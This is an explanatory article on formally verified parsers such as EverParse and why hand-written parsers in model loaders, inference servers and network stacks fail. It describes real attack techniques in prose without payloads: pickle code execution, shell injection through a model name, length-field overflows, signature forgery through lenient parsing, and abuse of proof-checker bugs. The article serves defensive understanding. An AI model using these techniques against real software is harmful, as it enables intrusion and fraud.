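# Verified parsers and serializers for model files and network inputs

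## What do AI systems parse, and why do hand-written parsers fail?

A parser is code that turns a string of bytes into structured values, or rejects it. Any program that opens a file or receives a network message contains one, often several, and the bytes may come from an attacker. A verified parser has a machine-checked proof that it accepts exactly the inputs its format description allows, without memory errors. Microsoft Research develops EverParse, a tool that generates such parsers. Swamy, Ramananandro and colleagues (2022) report in *Hardening Attack Surfaces with Formally Proven Binary Format Parsers* that its output has replaced hand-written code in the Windows kernel. AI systems also read a lot of data from untrusted sources. Whether verified parsers could replace hand-written ones in these systems depends on what the systems read and what goes wrong when they read it.

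### Basic terms

Suppose a program stores a name as one byte for the length, followed by that many letters, so "Ada" becomes four bytes, the number 3 and then the codes for A, d and a. A parser reads the four bytes and returns the text "Ada". A serializer does the reverse. A validator only checks whether the bytes fit the format, without building a structured copy of them. Deserialization means rebuilding program objects from stored or transmitted bytes, as when a training script reloads a saved neural network.

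Memory safety means that a program never reads or writes outside the memory that belongs to it. If a message gives its length as 200 bytes but contains only three letters, a parser that doesn't check the length will also copy 197 bytes of adjacent memory. An integer overflow occurs when a result is too large for the bits that hold it and wraps around to a small number. In 32-bit arithmetic, the total size of 1,073,741,825 four-byte items comes out as 4, so a program that uses this total to reserve memory reserves four bytes and then writes more than a billion items.

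Fuzzing means running a program on large numbers of generated inputs to find crashes. For example, a fuzzer might take the four bytes that encode "Ada", change some at random, and repeat this a few million times. *Secure Input Handling* (Poll, 2024), a set of university lecture notes, describes a student who accidentally found buffer overflows (writes past the end of a block of memory) in a contactless payment terminal. Poll thinks any fuzzer would have found them in seconds.

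A parser differential exists when two programs read the same bytes differently. Poll's example is a website certificate whose name field held PayPal's domain, then a zero byte, then an attacker's domain. The issuing authority read the whole field and identified the site as the attacker's, while Firefox and Internet Explorer stopped at the zero byte and identified it as PayPal's.

### What an AI system reads, and from whom

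An AI system first loads a checkpoint, the file that holds a model's trained weights. *On the (In)Security of Loading Machine Learning Models* (Digregorio, Di Gennaro and colleagues, 2025) counts over 2.1 million models on Hugging Face, an open hub where users publish and download them. A checkpoint's format determines which code reads it. PyTorch, a widely used framework for neural networks, saves checkpoints with pickle, Python's own object storage format, and Python's pickle code loads them. A safetensors file consists of a length, a header in JSON (a common text format for nested data) and the raw numbers. GGUF packs weights and metadata into one binary file for llama.cpp, a C and C++ program that runs language models on ordinary computers.

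Openwall's *Security Advisory* (2026) describes flaws in two GGUF readers, one in C++ and one in Python, and names Ollama and LM Studio among the projects that use the format. Many local AI products end up calling llama.cpp's core, so a parsing flaw there affects far more than one program. Programmers allocate and free memory by hand in that core, according to *Breaking Local AI Runtimes*, an audit by the security company Cyera. In their conference talk *AI Security at Scale*, Keys and Yuen explain that offsets, shapes and counts in a model file become allocation sizes, loop bounds and memory addresses. They also say that a file can parse successfully even if nobody has checked the relation between two fields that are each valid alone.

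A model's publisher supplies configuration and tokenizer files along with the weights. The configuration file describes the model's architecture, and the tokenizer file holds the vocabulary that software uses to split text into the numbered pieces the model processes. In Hugging Face's documented layout, a JSON file named tokenizer.json stores the vocabulary, and the hub's model libraries read it. GGUF stores the vocabulary inside the model file, so llama.cpp reads it with its own C++ code. OSV's *CVE-2025-49847* (2025), an entry in a public vulnerability database, records that a crafted vocabulary could overflow a buffer in that code.

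The model's publisher also supplies the chat template, which turns a conversation, stored as a list of messages with roles, into the single text that the model takes as input. Hugging Face's *Chat Templates* defines it as a snippet of Jinja2, a templating language with loops and conditions. The template of one small Qwen model, for instance, loops over the messages and inserts a default instruction if the conversation does not begin with one. The template engine has to parse a template and then run it.

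Once the model is loaded, requests arrive from users, who may be anyone able to reach the server's network port. In vLLM, an open-source server for language models, the access key protects only addresses that begin with /v1. Several other addresses, including one that runs the model, work without the key, according to vLLM's *Security* page. Web-server code and a JSON parser handle each request first. Images and audio then go to separate decoding libraries, whose security varies, as llama.cpp's *Security Policy* cautions. A user can also send vLLM a link to an image, which the server then downloads, so some of its input may come from the owner of another website.

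Attacks by this route can also use well-formed input. Zhao, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Continuous Discovery of Vulnerabilities in LLM Serving Systems with Fuzzing*, tested vLLM and a similar server, SGLang, with timed sequences of valid requests. They found 15 vulnerabilities, 10 of which the developers confirmed. A better parser would not have prevented one of them, in which the server reused stale cached state and sent a user a value from another user's request.

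The last kind of input is the messages that servers send each other when one model runs across several machines. Only those servers are supposed to send them, but vLLM relies partly on PyTorch's distributed features, which accept connections from anywhere without checks and send messages unencrypted. The vLLM developers therefore tell operators to put the machines on an isolated network. The code that receives the messages can be just as permissive. In an older vLLM engine, off by default since version 0.8.0, secondary machines deserialized messages from the primary one with pickle. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2017* records that the maintainers decided against a fix and recommended a secure network instead.

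### A missing check in Linux

Hand-written parsers fail in ways that look trivial afterwards. TCP, the protocol that carries most web traffic, puts a header in front of the data it sends. The header has a fixed part of 20 bytes, followed by a variable-length list of options. One field, the data offset, gives the header's total length in units of four bytes. Linux multiplies it by four and subtracts 20 to get the number of option bytes to read. Most options begin with one byte for their kind and one for their size, which the kernel uses to move its pointer to the next option. Two kinds, "end of list" and "no operation", are a single byte long. The sender of the packet sets all of these values and so controls how the kernel moves its pointer.

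Suppose the data offset is 6, which leaves four option bytes, and the sender fills them with three no-operations and the kind byte of a longer option. The kernel skips the three no-operations. Because one byte remains, the loop continues and reads the kind, then reads the size from the next byte, which lies outside the options. *ipv4* (Xiao, 2019), a patch sent to the kernel's developers in May 2019, added the missing two-line check, which returns if fewer than two bytes remain.

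The discussion of the patch suggests that this bug was harmless, although Swamy and colleagues open their paper with it as a possible out-of-bounds access in a file that had been in the kernel for at least 20 years. Eric Dumazet, who reviewed the patch, replied that at least 320 bytes of other kernel data follow the buffer, so the stray read lands in valid memory, and that the next two tests discard the result anyway. A size below 2 is illegal, and a size of 2 or more exceeds the one byte left. Nobody could tell that the read was harmless from the loop up to that line, and Dumazet approved the patch because it would make the code "obviously correct for all eyes". Two years later, Mikityanskiy (2021) found the same one-byte over-read in another of the kernel's hand-written parsers for the same options.

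Swamy and colleagues attribute the danger to the combination of pointer arithmetic over variable-length data and fields whose legal values depend on earlier fields. Programmers have to remember to write a separate check for each dependency, and well-formed traffic never exposes a missing check.

A memory-safe language such as Rust would prevent the out-of-bounds read. Poll considers switching languages the best single step, and cites Microsoft figures showing that roughly 70% of the security flaws the company fixed in 2019 were memory corruption. This is a strong argument, so verified parsers have to be justified by what they add beyond memory safety. In the talk *EverParse*, Ramananandro, one of the tool's developers, argues that Rust parsers can still panic at runtime (the program stops rather than read out of bounds) and can still have functional bugs, where the code runs safely but returns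 the wrong values.

### Recognize first, then process

The best-known general explanation of why hand-written parsers fail comes from language-theoretic security, or LangSec, a school that *Security Applications of Formal Language Theory* (Sassaman, Patterson and colleagues, 2011) helped to found. LangSec researchers treat the set of valid inputs to a program as a formal language, meaning a precisely defined set of strings. *Curing the Vulnerable Parser* (Bratus, Hermerschmidt and colleagues, 2017) presents the practical form of the argument.

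A program builds objects from its input, and the rest of the code makes assumptions about those objects. If the parser hasn't fully checked an assumption, an attacker can choose an input that violates it. In most software, the checks are scattered through the code, and the program starts using some fields before it has looked at others. Bratus and colleagues call this a shotgun parser. Nobody can say with confidence whether its checks cover the assumptions. They propose full recognition before processing, in which one component compares the entire input with a defined grammar, rejects whatever does not match, and only then passes objects to the rest of the program.

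The rule would have prevented Heartbleed, a flaw in the encryption library OpenSSL. A heartbeat message had its own length field and sat inside a record that also had one. The two lengths had to agree, but OpenSSL never compared them. An attacker could send a four-byte message that declared an inner length of 65,535, and the server would send back that many bytes of its memory.

Bratus and colleagues also want formats to be simpler. When length fields are nested, each must agree with the others and with the total, and the number of comparisons can grow with the square of the number of fields. This advice is hard to follow for anyone who has to read an existing format. TCP headers are full of such dependences, and so are model files, with their offsets and shapes. Bratus and colleagues also concede that generating the parser from a description does not by itself solve the problem. ASN.1, an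 older standard for describing message formats, came with code generators, yet a keyword search of public vulnerability records turned up 95 entries related to it. EverParse follows the LangSec rule but departs from the school on both points. Its description language can express fields that depend on other fields, and a proof covers the generated code.

### Mishandled data and executable content

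Some of the files that AI systems load can cause harm even when they are parsed correctly, and none of these remedies protects against that.

In the first kind of danger, the format describes only numbers, text and arrays, but the parser mishandles them. OSV's *CVE-2025-53630* (2025) describes an integer overflow in llama.cpp's GGUF parser that led to reads and writes outside the allocated memory. A correct parser would have rejected the file or loaded it safely.

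Other formats carry instructions for the loader to execute. A pickle file is a sequence of such instructions, one of which calls a function with arguments taken from the file. Hugging Face's *Pickle Scanning* page demonstrates a file that runs an attacker's command as soon as someone loads it. This involves no parsing error. The format allows the attacker's instruction, so even a parser proved correct would pass it on. Poll also distinguishes attacks that exploit bugs from attacks that exploit features.

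Researchers on model security often divide file formats into those that hold data and those that hold code, which Digregorio and colleagues call data-based and code-based. *DITTO* (2026), a paper on scanning pickle files, classifies GGUF, safetensors and Protocol Buffers (Google's general-purpose binary encoding) as data-based. These labels are useful but can mislead. The framework Keras describes a model's structure in JSON, a data-based format, yet the file may contain a layer with embedded Python bytecode, which runs on loading if the user has switched off safe mode. TensorFlow's SavedModel format uses Protocol Buffers, but Digregorio and colleagues list it as permitting arbitrary code execution by design, since the file encodes a graph of operations. Classifying a format therefore requires knowing what the program does with the parsed values, not just how the bytes are laid out.

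Bratus questioned whether there is any line between data and programs. He said in Dark Reading's *Taming Bad Inputs Means Taking Aim At 'Weird Machines'* that code that handles complex data behaves like a virtual machine, "making any input a program". This is a fair description of how attackers work, but the line still holds for verification, because a format specification can forbid the accidental computation that a buffer overflow makes possible, whereas the pickle specification provides for function calls.

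Executable content can also appear in a program's output, so serializers matter too. *Breaking AI Inference Systems*, by Ventuzelo and Benazzouz, describes an attack on Triton, NVIDIA's model server, that used only a model's name. Triton pasted the name into a command for the operating system's shell, so an attacker could take control of the machine with a name that closed the expected argument and added another command. A parser for the incoming request would have accepted the name as ordinary text unless the format restricted what names may contain. Bratus and colleagues propose an "unparser" for this situation, a serializer that follows the output's grammar and encodes special characters so that the receiving program reads them as text.

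## What does a proof about a parser establish, and what must still be trusted?

A parser and a serializer for the same format should undo each other. Proving that they do requires defining both as mathematical functions. *Secure Parsing and Serializing with Separation Logic* (Ramananandro, Ebner et al., 2025) defines a parser p as a function that takes a string of bytes b and returns either failure or a pair (v, n), where v is the value and n is the number of bytes consumed. Given the four bytes that encode "Ada" and its length, p returns ("Ada", 4), even if other data follows. A serializer s takes a value and returns bytes.

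The function p is the format specification. It defines which byte strings are valid and what they mean. It can be slow, because nobody runs it in the finished product. Researchers prove that p has useful properties, and then that the fast code agrees with p.

### Round trips, non-malleability and the validator theorem

The round-trip property is:

p(s(v)) = (v, length of s(v)), for every value v.

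In words, a program that serializes a value and parses the result gets the same value back, with no bytes left over. Non-malleability concerns the opposite direction:

If p(b) = (v, n), then s(v) = the first n bytes of b.

In words, the parser accepts no byte string for v except the one that the serializer writes.

Ramananandro and colleagues define non-malleability without a serializer. If p returns the same v for two inputs, it must have consumed the same sequence of bytes from each. For a format with the round-trip property, the two definitions are equivalent. Suppose p(b) = (v, n). By the round-trip property, p also returns v for the input s(v) and consumes all of it, so their definition requires the first n bytes of b to be s(v). Conversely, if the bytes consumed from every input that yields v are s(v), then p consumes the same bytes from any two such inputs.

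The validator theorem connects p to the code that runs. If f is that code, then:

f(b) = n exactly when p(b) = (v, n) for some v, and f(b) fails exactly when p(b) fails.

The proof must show both that the code accepts every valid input and that it rejects every invalid one, since code that accepts everything would meet the first requirement and code that rejects everything would meet the second. If the code also returns values, a further theorem must show that each one equals the specified value v.

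Most formats are built from smaller ones, and combining them requires one more property. To store a pair, a serializer writes s1(v1) and then s2(v2). If the parser for the first value reads text until the input ends, it will read the second value too. The round trip then fails for the pair, although it holds for each part. Ramananandro and colleagues therefore require the first parser to have the prefix property: if p(b) = (v, n), then p returns the same result for every input that begins with the same n bytes.

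### Two encodings of the number 5

Many binary formats write small integers in fewer bytes. In one common scheme, which Protocol Buffers uses, the top bit of each byte is a flag that is 1 if another byte follows. The other seven bits hold a digit in base 128, with the least significant digit first. The byte 05 has flag 0 and digit 5, so it means 5. In the two bytes 85 00, the first has flag 1 and digit 5, and the second has flag 0 and digit 0. Their value is 5 + 0 × 128, which is also 5.

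A sensible serializer writes 5 as the single byte 05, so s(5) = 05. The round trip holds, because p(05) = (5, 1). Non-malleability fails, because p(85 00) = (5, 2) and the two bytes consumed, 85 00, differ from s(5). The longer strings 85 80 00 and 85 80 80 00 also parse to 5. A programmer who tests the code by serializing numbers and parsing them again won't notice this failure, because that test succeeds for every number.

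The format can be fixed by making the parser reject any encoding longer than one byte that ends in 00. The last byte holds the number's leading digit in base 128, so this rule forbids leading zeros and leaves each number with only one encoding.

Bitcoin's format has an integer type with the same weakness. An integer takes one, three, five or nine bytes, depending on the first byte, so 4,636 fits into three bytes but could also fill five. Ramananandro's 2019 paper on EverParse points out that the documentation left unclear whether the longer form was legal. The main Bitcoin program does enforce the shortest form. When daira reported the gap in *Documentation omission* (2016), a developer recalled that the program had not always enforced the rule. It had instead re-serialized blocks before checks that depended on their encoded size. The developers later began rejecting the longer forms, partly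 to make the program's correctness more obvious.

Malleability matters when a program computes a hash, a short fingerprint of some bytes, but people care about the values those bytes represent. The hashes of 05 and 85 00 differ. Bitcoin identifies a transaction by the hash of its serialized form, and the format originally allowed several encodings of the signature inside. An attacker could re-encode the signature in somebody's transaction and have the network confirm it under another identifier. The sender, looking for the original identifier, might conclude that the payment had failed. The exchange Mt. Gox blamed this attack for the loss of over 850,000 bitcoins. Others dispute that, but a later analysis, cited in Ramananandro's paper, found that 30,000 transactions worth a total of 300,000 bitcoins were confirmed under a changed identifier in February 2014.

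Lenient parsing can also let an attacker forge signatures. In one older scheme, RSA signatures with exponent 3, the verifier cubes the signature modulo a large public number. The result must consist of fixed padding followed by a small structure containing the message's hash. The padding fills almost the whole number, which leaves an attacker very little freedom. But some verifiers ignored any bytes after the structure. An attacker could then shorten the padding, place the hash of any message right after it and let the remaining bytes take any value. So many numbers are then acceptable that one of them is a perfect cube, and its ordinary cube root is a valid signature. A parser should therefore return n, because the caller has to compare it with the length of the input.

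According to Ramananandro's paper, the attack has reappeared in dozens of implementations. Lenient signature parsers still turn up. *libgcrypt P256 signature malleability via weak DER enforcement*, a report from January 2026, describes a cryptographic library that accepts signatures whose numbers have unnecessary leading zeros, much like 85 00. Programs that check the hash of the file exactly as it arrived, before parsing it, do not depend on non-malleability in this way.

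### Safety properties with separate proofs

Verified parsers come with several theorems because neither memory safety nor functional correctness implies the other. A function that rejects every input never reads out of bounds and always terminates, but it is useless as a parser, and a proof of functional correctness rules it out. Code can also return the right answer and still read a byte out of bounds along the way, as Linux did when parsing TCP options.

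The memory-safety theorem for a validator in C applies only if the caller passes a pointer to a buffer and a length no greater than the buffer's real size. The code then reads only inside the buffer and writes only to the locations that its interface lists.

Arithmetic safety means that no calculation overflows or underflows. Swamy and colleagues give the example of a format with two 32-bit numbers, in which the second must be at least n greater than the first. The obvious check is second − first ≥ n. If the first number is 10 and the second is 3, the subtraction wraps around to 4,294,967,289 and the check passes for almost any n, although no memory error has occurred yet. EverParse rejects this description until its author adds a test, before the subtraction, that the first number does not exceed the second.

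Termination means that the code finishes on every input. A list parser repeats the parser for one element until the input runs out. If the element parser consumed zero bytes, the loop would never end. EverParse's library makes the list parser fail in that case, so every successful round leaves fewer bytes and the loop must eventually stop.

All of these theorems treat b as fixed. If another program can write to the same memory, the parser might check a length, then get a different number when it reads the length again to use it. A parser free of double fetches reads no byte more than once, so the bytes it has read form a single string b, to which the other theorems apply. Swamy and colleagues prove this property by modeling the input as a stream in which reading a byte uses up the permission to read it.

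The proofs don't cover how long the code takes to run. EverParse's code branches on values from the input, and Ramananandro et al. warn that its timing could leak confidential data.

### How a computer checks a proof

A proof assistant is a program that checks every step of a proof written in a formal language. Lean, Coq and F* are proof assistants that are also programming languages, so a programmer can write a parser and the theorem about it in the same language.

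In slides on EverParse, Ramananandro shows a small F* function that multiplies a 32-bit number `a` by 9. It shifts `a` left by three bits, which multiplies it by 8, then adds the original `a`. The programmer declares the precondition that 9 × `a` fits into 32 bits and the postcondition that the result equals 9 × `a`. F* accepts the function only if the postcondition follows from the precondition and the code. It accepts a call to the function only where it can prove that `a` is at most 477,218,588.

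Writing out every step of such proofs by hand would take too long, so F* translates whatever remains to be shown into logical formulas and passes them to Z3, an automated solver. Z3 looks for values that would make a formula false, and the proof succeeds if Z3 establishes that none exist. Lean's automation normally has to produce a complete proof, which a smaller program called the kernel then checks. With a solver, people write less but must trust a larger program.

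### The trusted computing base

The trusted computing base is everything that must be right for a proof to mean what people take it to mean. For EverParse, Swamy and colleagues list F*, Z3, the front end that reads format descriptions, and KaRaMeL, which translates F* into C. The C compiler, the operating system and the hardware are also part of it.

*An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues, 2017) examined how such assumptions fail in IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar, three research systems that keep copies of data consistent across several servers and have machine-checked proofs. The study found 16 bugs. Eleven were in the "shim layer", which connects the proved code to the network and the disk. Three were in verification tools and two were in specifications.

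Fonseca and colleagues searched for more than eight months and found no mistakes in how the verified systems implemented their protocols, which the proofs covered. One year of bug reports for four widely used unverified systems included 12 protocol bugs. They caution against comparing the counts directly, because the unverified systems are larger and have far more users. But protocols are notoriously hard to implement, so finding no such bugs is good evidence that the proofs worked.

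A more recent case is lean-zip, a version of the compression library zlib that ten AI agents wrote and proved correct in Lean. kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes a 2026 test of it. The author removed the theorems and documentation so that Claude, the AI agent running the test, would not know the code was verified. Claude launched 16 fuzzers, which ran for about 19 hours and executed the code 105,823,818 times. Four inputs caused crashes, but Claude found no memory error in the library's Lean code.

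This is weaker evidence for proofs than it looks, because Lean is a memory-safe language and even an unproved Lean program should not have such errors. The testing tools looked for crashes, memory errors and undefined behavior, so they would have missed incorrect output. The author did find two bugs, one in Lean's runtime and one in a part of lean-zip that had no proofs.

### Incomplete specifications

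IronFleet's specification did not require a server to execute a request only once if the network delivered it twice. The code handled duplicates correctly anyway, but after Fonseca and colleagues changed seven lines to disable this protection, it still passed verification. IronFleet's developers replied that they had known about the omission and did not consider it a bug. In Chapar, an assertion in an example client checked the same condition as the branch containing it, so it could never fail.

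EverParse proves certain properties, such as memory safety, for every format description, so a mistake in a description cannot break them. The mistake can still harm an application that relies on a constraint the description's author forgot to write down. For example, if a description does not require a range to start before it ends, the parser will pass on a reversed range, and the application may compute a length from it that wraps around to a huge number. Ramananandro et al. (2019) are therefore too optimistic when they argue that, at worst, a mistake makes the generated messages incompatible with other people's software.

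A true theorem can also cover less than its name suggests. One of lean-zip's main theorems is a round trip, meaning that decompressing its compressor's output returns the original data, for any data smaller than one gigabyte. A compressor and a decompressor that both left the data unchanged would satisfy it. It also does not cover malformed files, which the compressor never produces but an attacker would. A round trip alone would therefore be little protection for a loader that reads files from strangers, though other proofs in the project deal with parts of the compression format.

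### Faulty proof checkers

IronFleet's build tool sometimes accepted programs without a proof. When Z3 crashed, the tool failed to detect the error message and reported success, even for a program that asserted something false. Fonseca and colleagues discovered this because the copy of Z3 in IronFleet's package could not start, since the package combined a 64-bit program with 32-bit libraries.

The serious tool bugs in their study lay outside the part that reasons about proofs, but Lean's kernel, which checks proofs, has also had a serious bug. Brossard (2026), in *Lean 4 kernel soundness bug*, explains how a malicious program could make the kernel accept a proof of 0 = 1 that used no axioms. When an expression extracted a field from a data structure, the kernel failed to check that the expression named the right structure. On July 25, 2026, somebody used the bug to publish a supposed disproof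 of the Collatz conjecture, a famous open problem about whole numbers. Nanoda, an independently written checker, also accepted the proof. A fix was available four days after the disproof was published.

Such a proof is unlikely to be written by accident, because the attack needs an engineered collision between two hashes and the attacker's code has to run while Lean builds the project. The risk is small for a team that proves its own parser, but greater for people who accept proofs from strangers or from AI systems trained to get proofs accepted. Leonardo de Moura, Lean's creator, expects more cases because "AIs are really good at exploiting soundness bugs in the kernels".

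### Compilers and runtimes

A proof in F* or Lean covers source code, which a compiler must still translate. Researchers proved KaRaMeL's design correct on paper, but the tool has no machine-checked proof. To compile C to machine code, programmers can use CompCert, which is largely verified. Fonseca and colleagues cite tests of 11 compilers that found more than 325 bugs, 11 of them in CompCert. According to kirancodes.me, the tests found bugs in CompCert's unverified front end but none in its proved optimization passes.

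In Ramananandro's 2019 paper, EverParse's validator for Bitcoin data ran 42% slower when compiled with CompCert than with the usual optimizing compilers. The alternative is to use an ordinary compiler and test the result. In the same paper, fuzzing the validator's machine code with more than 21 million inputs found no bugs.

Compiled code can also differ from the definition used in the proof. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) describes a Lean function that extracts part of a string. When the function is asked for one byte at an enormously high position, its logical definition gives an empty string, but the compiled version returned the entire original string. Lean has an option that lets proofs use the results of compiled code, and the security company used it to derive a contradiction and, from that, a bogus proof of Fermat's Last Theorem.

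Trail of Bits stresses that the kernel was not at fault and that Lean lists the use of compiled code among the proof's axioms, so a careful reader could spot the trick. The mismatch would matter for a parser even if nobody had used it to prove anything false, because parsers routinely extract pieces of their input. A theorem about such a parser would apply to the definition, while users would run the compiled version.

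The memory error found in the lean-zip test also lay below the proved code, in Lean's runtime, the C++ code that supports every compiled Lean program. To reserve memory for an array of bytes, the runtime adds 24 to the requested size. If the request is for 2^64 − 1 bytes, the largest number that 64 bits can hold, the sum wraps around to 23. The runtime then reserves only 23 bytes, and the program reads a whole file into them. A 156-byte ZIP file could trigger the overflow, and the bug affected every version of Lean 4 up to that time.

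### Surrounding code and limited resources

That ZIP file could reach the runtime because lean-zip had verified the compression algorithm, which is the difficult part, but not the archive reader. The reader took the compressed size from the file's header and requested that much memory without comparing it with the size of the file. A header that declared several exabytes made the program run out of memory and crash. The standard unzip program checks the size first. A format specification that required the data to fit inside the file would have ruled out both attacks.

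Fonseca and colleagues found much the same, with five of the 11 shim-layer bugs involving communication. Verdi's server crashed when a single read from the network returned only part of a request. Verdi also separated commands and arguments with line breaks and spaces but did not encode those characters inside arguments, so a client could hide a second command inside the first. Trying to prove the round-trip property would have exposed this bug, because the server parsed something other than what the client's software had serialized.

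Even a fully verified parser depends on the program that calls it. If C code passes a length greater than the buffer's real size, the memory-safety theorem doesn't apply and the parser may read beyond the buffer's end. The theorem also doesn't apply if the code passes a pointer to memory that the program has already freed. Testers can focus on these interfaces between verified and unverified code. Fonseca and colleagues built tests for such interfaces that detect 13 of the 16 bugs they found.

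Developers and their critics don't always agree on where the verified code ends. Symbolic Software published *We Found Bugs in CE Labs' Verified Code* in February 2026, after the disclosure of five vulnerabilities in cryptographic libraries, including libcrux. CE Labs, which maintains the libraries, replied that nobody had yet found a bug in the verified code. Whether the bugs were in verified code matters for judging the method, but much less to a user whose program calls the whole library.

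Many proofs also ignore memory limits. Verdi's server crashed with a stack overflow when another server had fallen more than 500,000 requests behind. A function in the proved code called itself once for every missing request, and each call used some of the stack, the memory that holds unfinished function calls. The proof did not account for the stack's size.

Developers can include such limits in the theorem. Slides from Lean (2026) show a later version of lean-zip's round-trip theorem in which the decompressor takes a maximum output size, and the guarantee applies to data up to that size. Swamy and colleagues prove that their validators reserve no memory on the heap, which holds data whose size a program determines while it runs. If a format lets values contain other values, an attacker could exhaust the stack with thousands of nested layers. Ramananandro and colleagues designed their 2025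 library to parse such data with a fixed amount of stack, however deep the nesting.

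## How does EverParse turn a format description into proved code?

EverParse's developers proved these theorems once, for a library of small building blocks. A user describes a format in a language similar to C's type definitions, and EverParse assembles a parser from the blocks. The user writes no proofs, which matters because few projects would have time to prove the theorems by hand for every format they read.

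### LowParse and the languages built on it

The library, LowParse, is a collection of F* combinators, which are functions that build larger parsers out of smaller ones. For example, parse_pair takes two parsers p1 and p2 and returns a parser that runs p1, runs p2 on the bytes that p1 left over, and returns both values. Ramananandro and colleagues explain that the combined parser is non-malleable if p1 and p2 are. Other combinators handle lists, bit fields and values that have to pass a test. If a format is built only from combinators, its theorems follow from the theorems about those combinators.

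Each combinator has a specification and an implementation. The specification is a pure function on byte sequences and helps to define p. The implementation works on real memory and comes with a proof that it agrees with the specification. For example, the implementation that validates a pair runs the first validator and, if that succeeds, starts the second one where the first stopped. Other implementation combinators skip over a valid item, read an integer or locate one part of a larger value.

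PulseParse, a newer version of these implementations, uses separation logic, which tracks which part of a program may use which part of memory. Its function for splitting a pair takes the array that holds the pair and returns two smaller arrays, one for each component, without copying any data. The caller gives up the right to use the whole array and regains it by handing back both parts. Proofs about such functions no longer have to track byte offsets.

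Several front ends translate format descriptions into calls to LowParse. EverParse's home page, Project Everest's *Verified efficient parsing for binary data formats*, lists three of them. QuackyDucky accepts a notation common in internet standards, and people have used it to generate message-processing code for TLS and QUIC, two protocols for encrypted connections. 3D is for C programs. EverCDDL, which is still experimental, accepts schemas for CBOR, a binary format for JSON-like data.

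KaRaMeL then translates the F* code into C. Ramananandro reports that it can now also produce Rust, and EverCDDL offers both languages. However, the 3D manual for releases since May 2025, Project Everest's *3d*, lists only C files as output.

### The 3D language

3D stands for "Dependent Data Descriptions", because the type or the legal values of one field may depend on earlier fields. Swamy and colleagues summarize the language in one line:

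t ::= b | x:t{e} | x:t0 & t1 | if e then t0 else t1

The letter b stands for a base type. Base types include unsigned integers of one, two, four or eight bytes in either byte order; unit, which takes up no bytes and always succeeds; and ⊥, which always fails.

The second form, x:t{e}, is a refinement. It contains the values x of type t for which the test e is true. In 3D notation, a month field might be written `UINT8 month { 1 <= month && month <= 12 }`. The generated parser rejects a message in which this byte is 13.

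The third form is a dependent pair, in which the type of the second part may use the value of the first. The format that stores "Ada" as a length and three letters needs one:

```
typedef struct _NAME {
  UINT8 len;
  UINT8 letters[:byte-size len];
} NAME;
```

The notation `[:byte-size len]` describes an array that fills exactly `len` bytes. 3D measures arrays in bytes because their elements may differ in length, so a count of elements would not determine where the array ends.

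The last form, the casetype, chooses between types and resembles a C union with an explicit switch. In TCP, for instance, the kind byte of an option determines what follows it, and a timestamp option must declare a length of 10. If no case matches and there is no default, the type is ⊥ and the parser rejects the input.

Types can also take parameters. The description of a TCP header takes the segment's length as a parameter from the calling program. It requires the header's length, which is four times the data offset, to be at least 20 bytes and at most the segment's length, and it gives the options array exactly the header's bytes after the first 20. In the malformed header that Linux over-read, the array ends where the last option's size byte should be, so the parser rejects the header without anyone having to remember to write the check that Linux lacked.

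A format description can still omit other requirements. For example, the TCP description in Project Everest's *3d lang*, the language reference, allows an end-of-list option in the middle of the list. *3d lang* acknowledges this weakness and says it was kept for simplicity.

Finally, a format description can attach actions to fields. An action is a short piece of code that runs as soon as the parser has validated the field. It can store a value or a pointer in one of the caller's variables, call a C function, or make the parser reject the input.

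A struct with a one-byte field followed by a four-byte field takes up five bytes in 3D, but C compilers usually insert three unused bytes between the fields. This difference matters because many programs validate a message and then treat the same bytes as a C struct. Programmers can ask 3D to insert the padding, in which case EverParse also generates assertions that make compilation fail if the C compiler's layout differs.

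### A table with a count and an offset

Swamy and colleagues describe a message from Hyper-V's networking code that contains a table of 32-bit numbers. It begins with three four-byte fields: the message type, the number of entries (Count) and the distance from the start of the message to the table (Offset). Unused bytes may separate these fields from the table. The message type belongs to an enclosing structure, so the description starts with Count. With a count of 16 as an example, it looks roughly like this:

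```
typedef struct _TABLE(UINT32 MaxSize, mutable PUINT8 *out) {
  UINT32 Count  { Count == 16 };
  UINT32 Offset { is_range_okay(MaxSize, Offset, 4 * Count)
                  && Offset >= 12 };
  UINT8  padding[:byte-size Offset - 12];
  UINT32 Table[:byte-size 4 * Count]
         {:act var p = field_ptr; *out = p; };
} TABLE;
```

MaxSize is the size of the whole message. The library function is_range_okay(size, offset, extent) stands for this test:

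extent ≤ size && offset ≤ size − extent

In a message of 100 bytes, the sixteen entries take up 64, so the table can start no later than byte 36. It can't start before byte 12, because it would overlap the first three fields. If Offset is 20, there are 8 bytes of padding, and the table occupies bytes 20 to 83.

Writing the test as offset + extent ≤ size would be unsafe because the 32-bit addition can wrap around. An attacker could set Offset to 4,294,967,292, which is 4 less than 2^32. Adding 64 would then give 60, and the test would pass even though the table would start almost 4 GiB away. The library's test avoids the addition, but its subtraction can also wrap around. If the message has only 40 bytes, 40 − 64 becomes 4,294,967,272, and nearly every offset passes.

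The order of the two comparisons prevents underflow. As in C, && evaluates its right side only if the left side is true, so the subtraction runs only when extent ≤ size. F* likewise assumes the left side is true when proving that the right side cannot underflow.

If the author swapped the comparisons, F* would reject the description. The swapped test would still give the right answer in C, because extent ≤ size would fail even after the subtraction wrapped around. But F* requires every operation to be safe when it runs, so reviewers don't have to work out whether a later test makes up for an earlier overflow.

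The remaining arithmetic has to meet the same standard. Offset − 12 is safe because the parser has already checked that Offset is at least 12, and 4 × Count is safe because Count is fixed. If Count could vary, the product could wrap around, so F* would require a bound. Count ≤ MaxSize / 4 would be enough, because it keeps the product from exceeding MaxSize.

An author who forgot the `is_range_okay` check would still get a memory-safe parser, because the generated code also checks that enough input remains for each array. But if the buffer held more than one message, the parser might accept a table that ran past the end of the message into the data after it.

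The action on the last line makes the caller's variable `out` point to the table, so the rest of the program never has to compute an address from Offset.

### Three meanings for each description

The front end turns a description into a data structure in F* that mirrors the one-line grammar, with one kind of node for pairs, another for refinements and so on. Swamy and colleagues define three functions on this structure. The function as_type returns the type of values the format can represent, as_parser returns the specification p, and as_validator returns a procedure that checks bytes in memory and runs the actions.

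| Description | Type | Parser | Validator |
|---|---|---|---|
| t1 followed by t2 | pairs of values | parse_pair | validate_pair |
| t with a test f | values of t that pass f | parse_filter | validate_filter |

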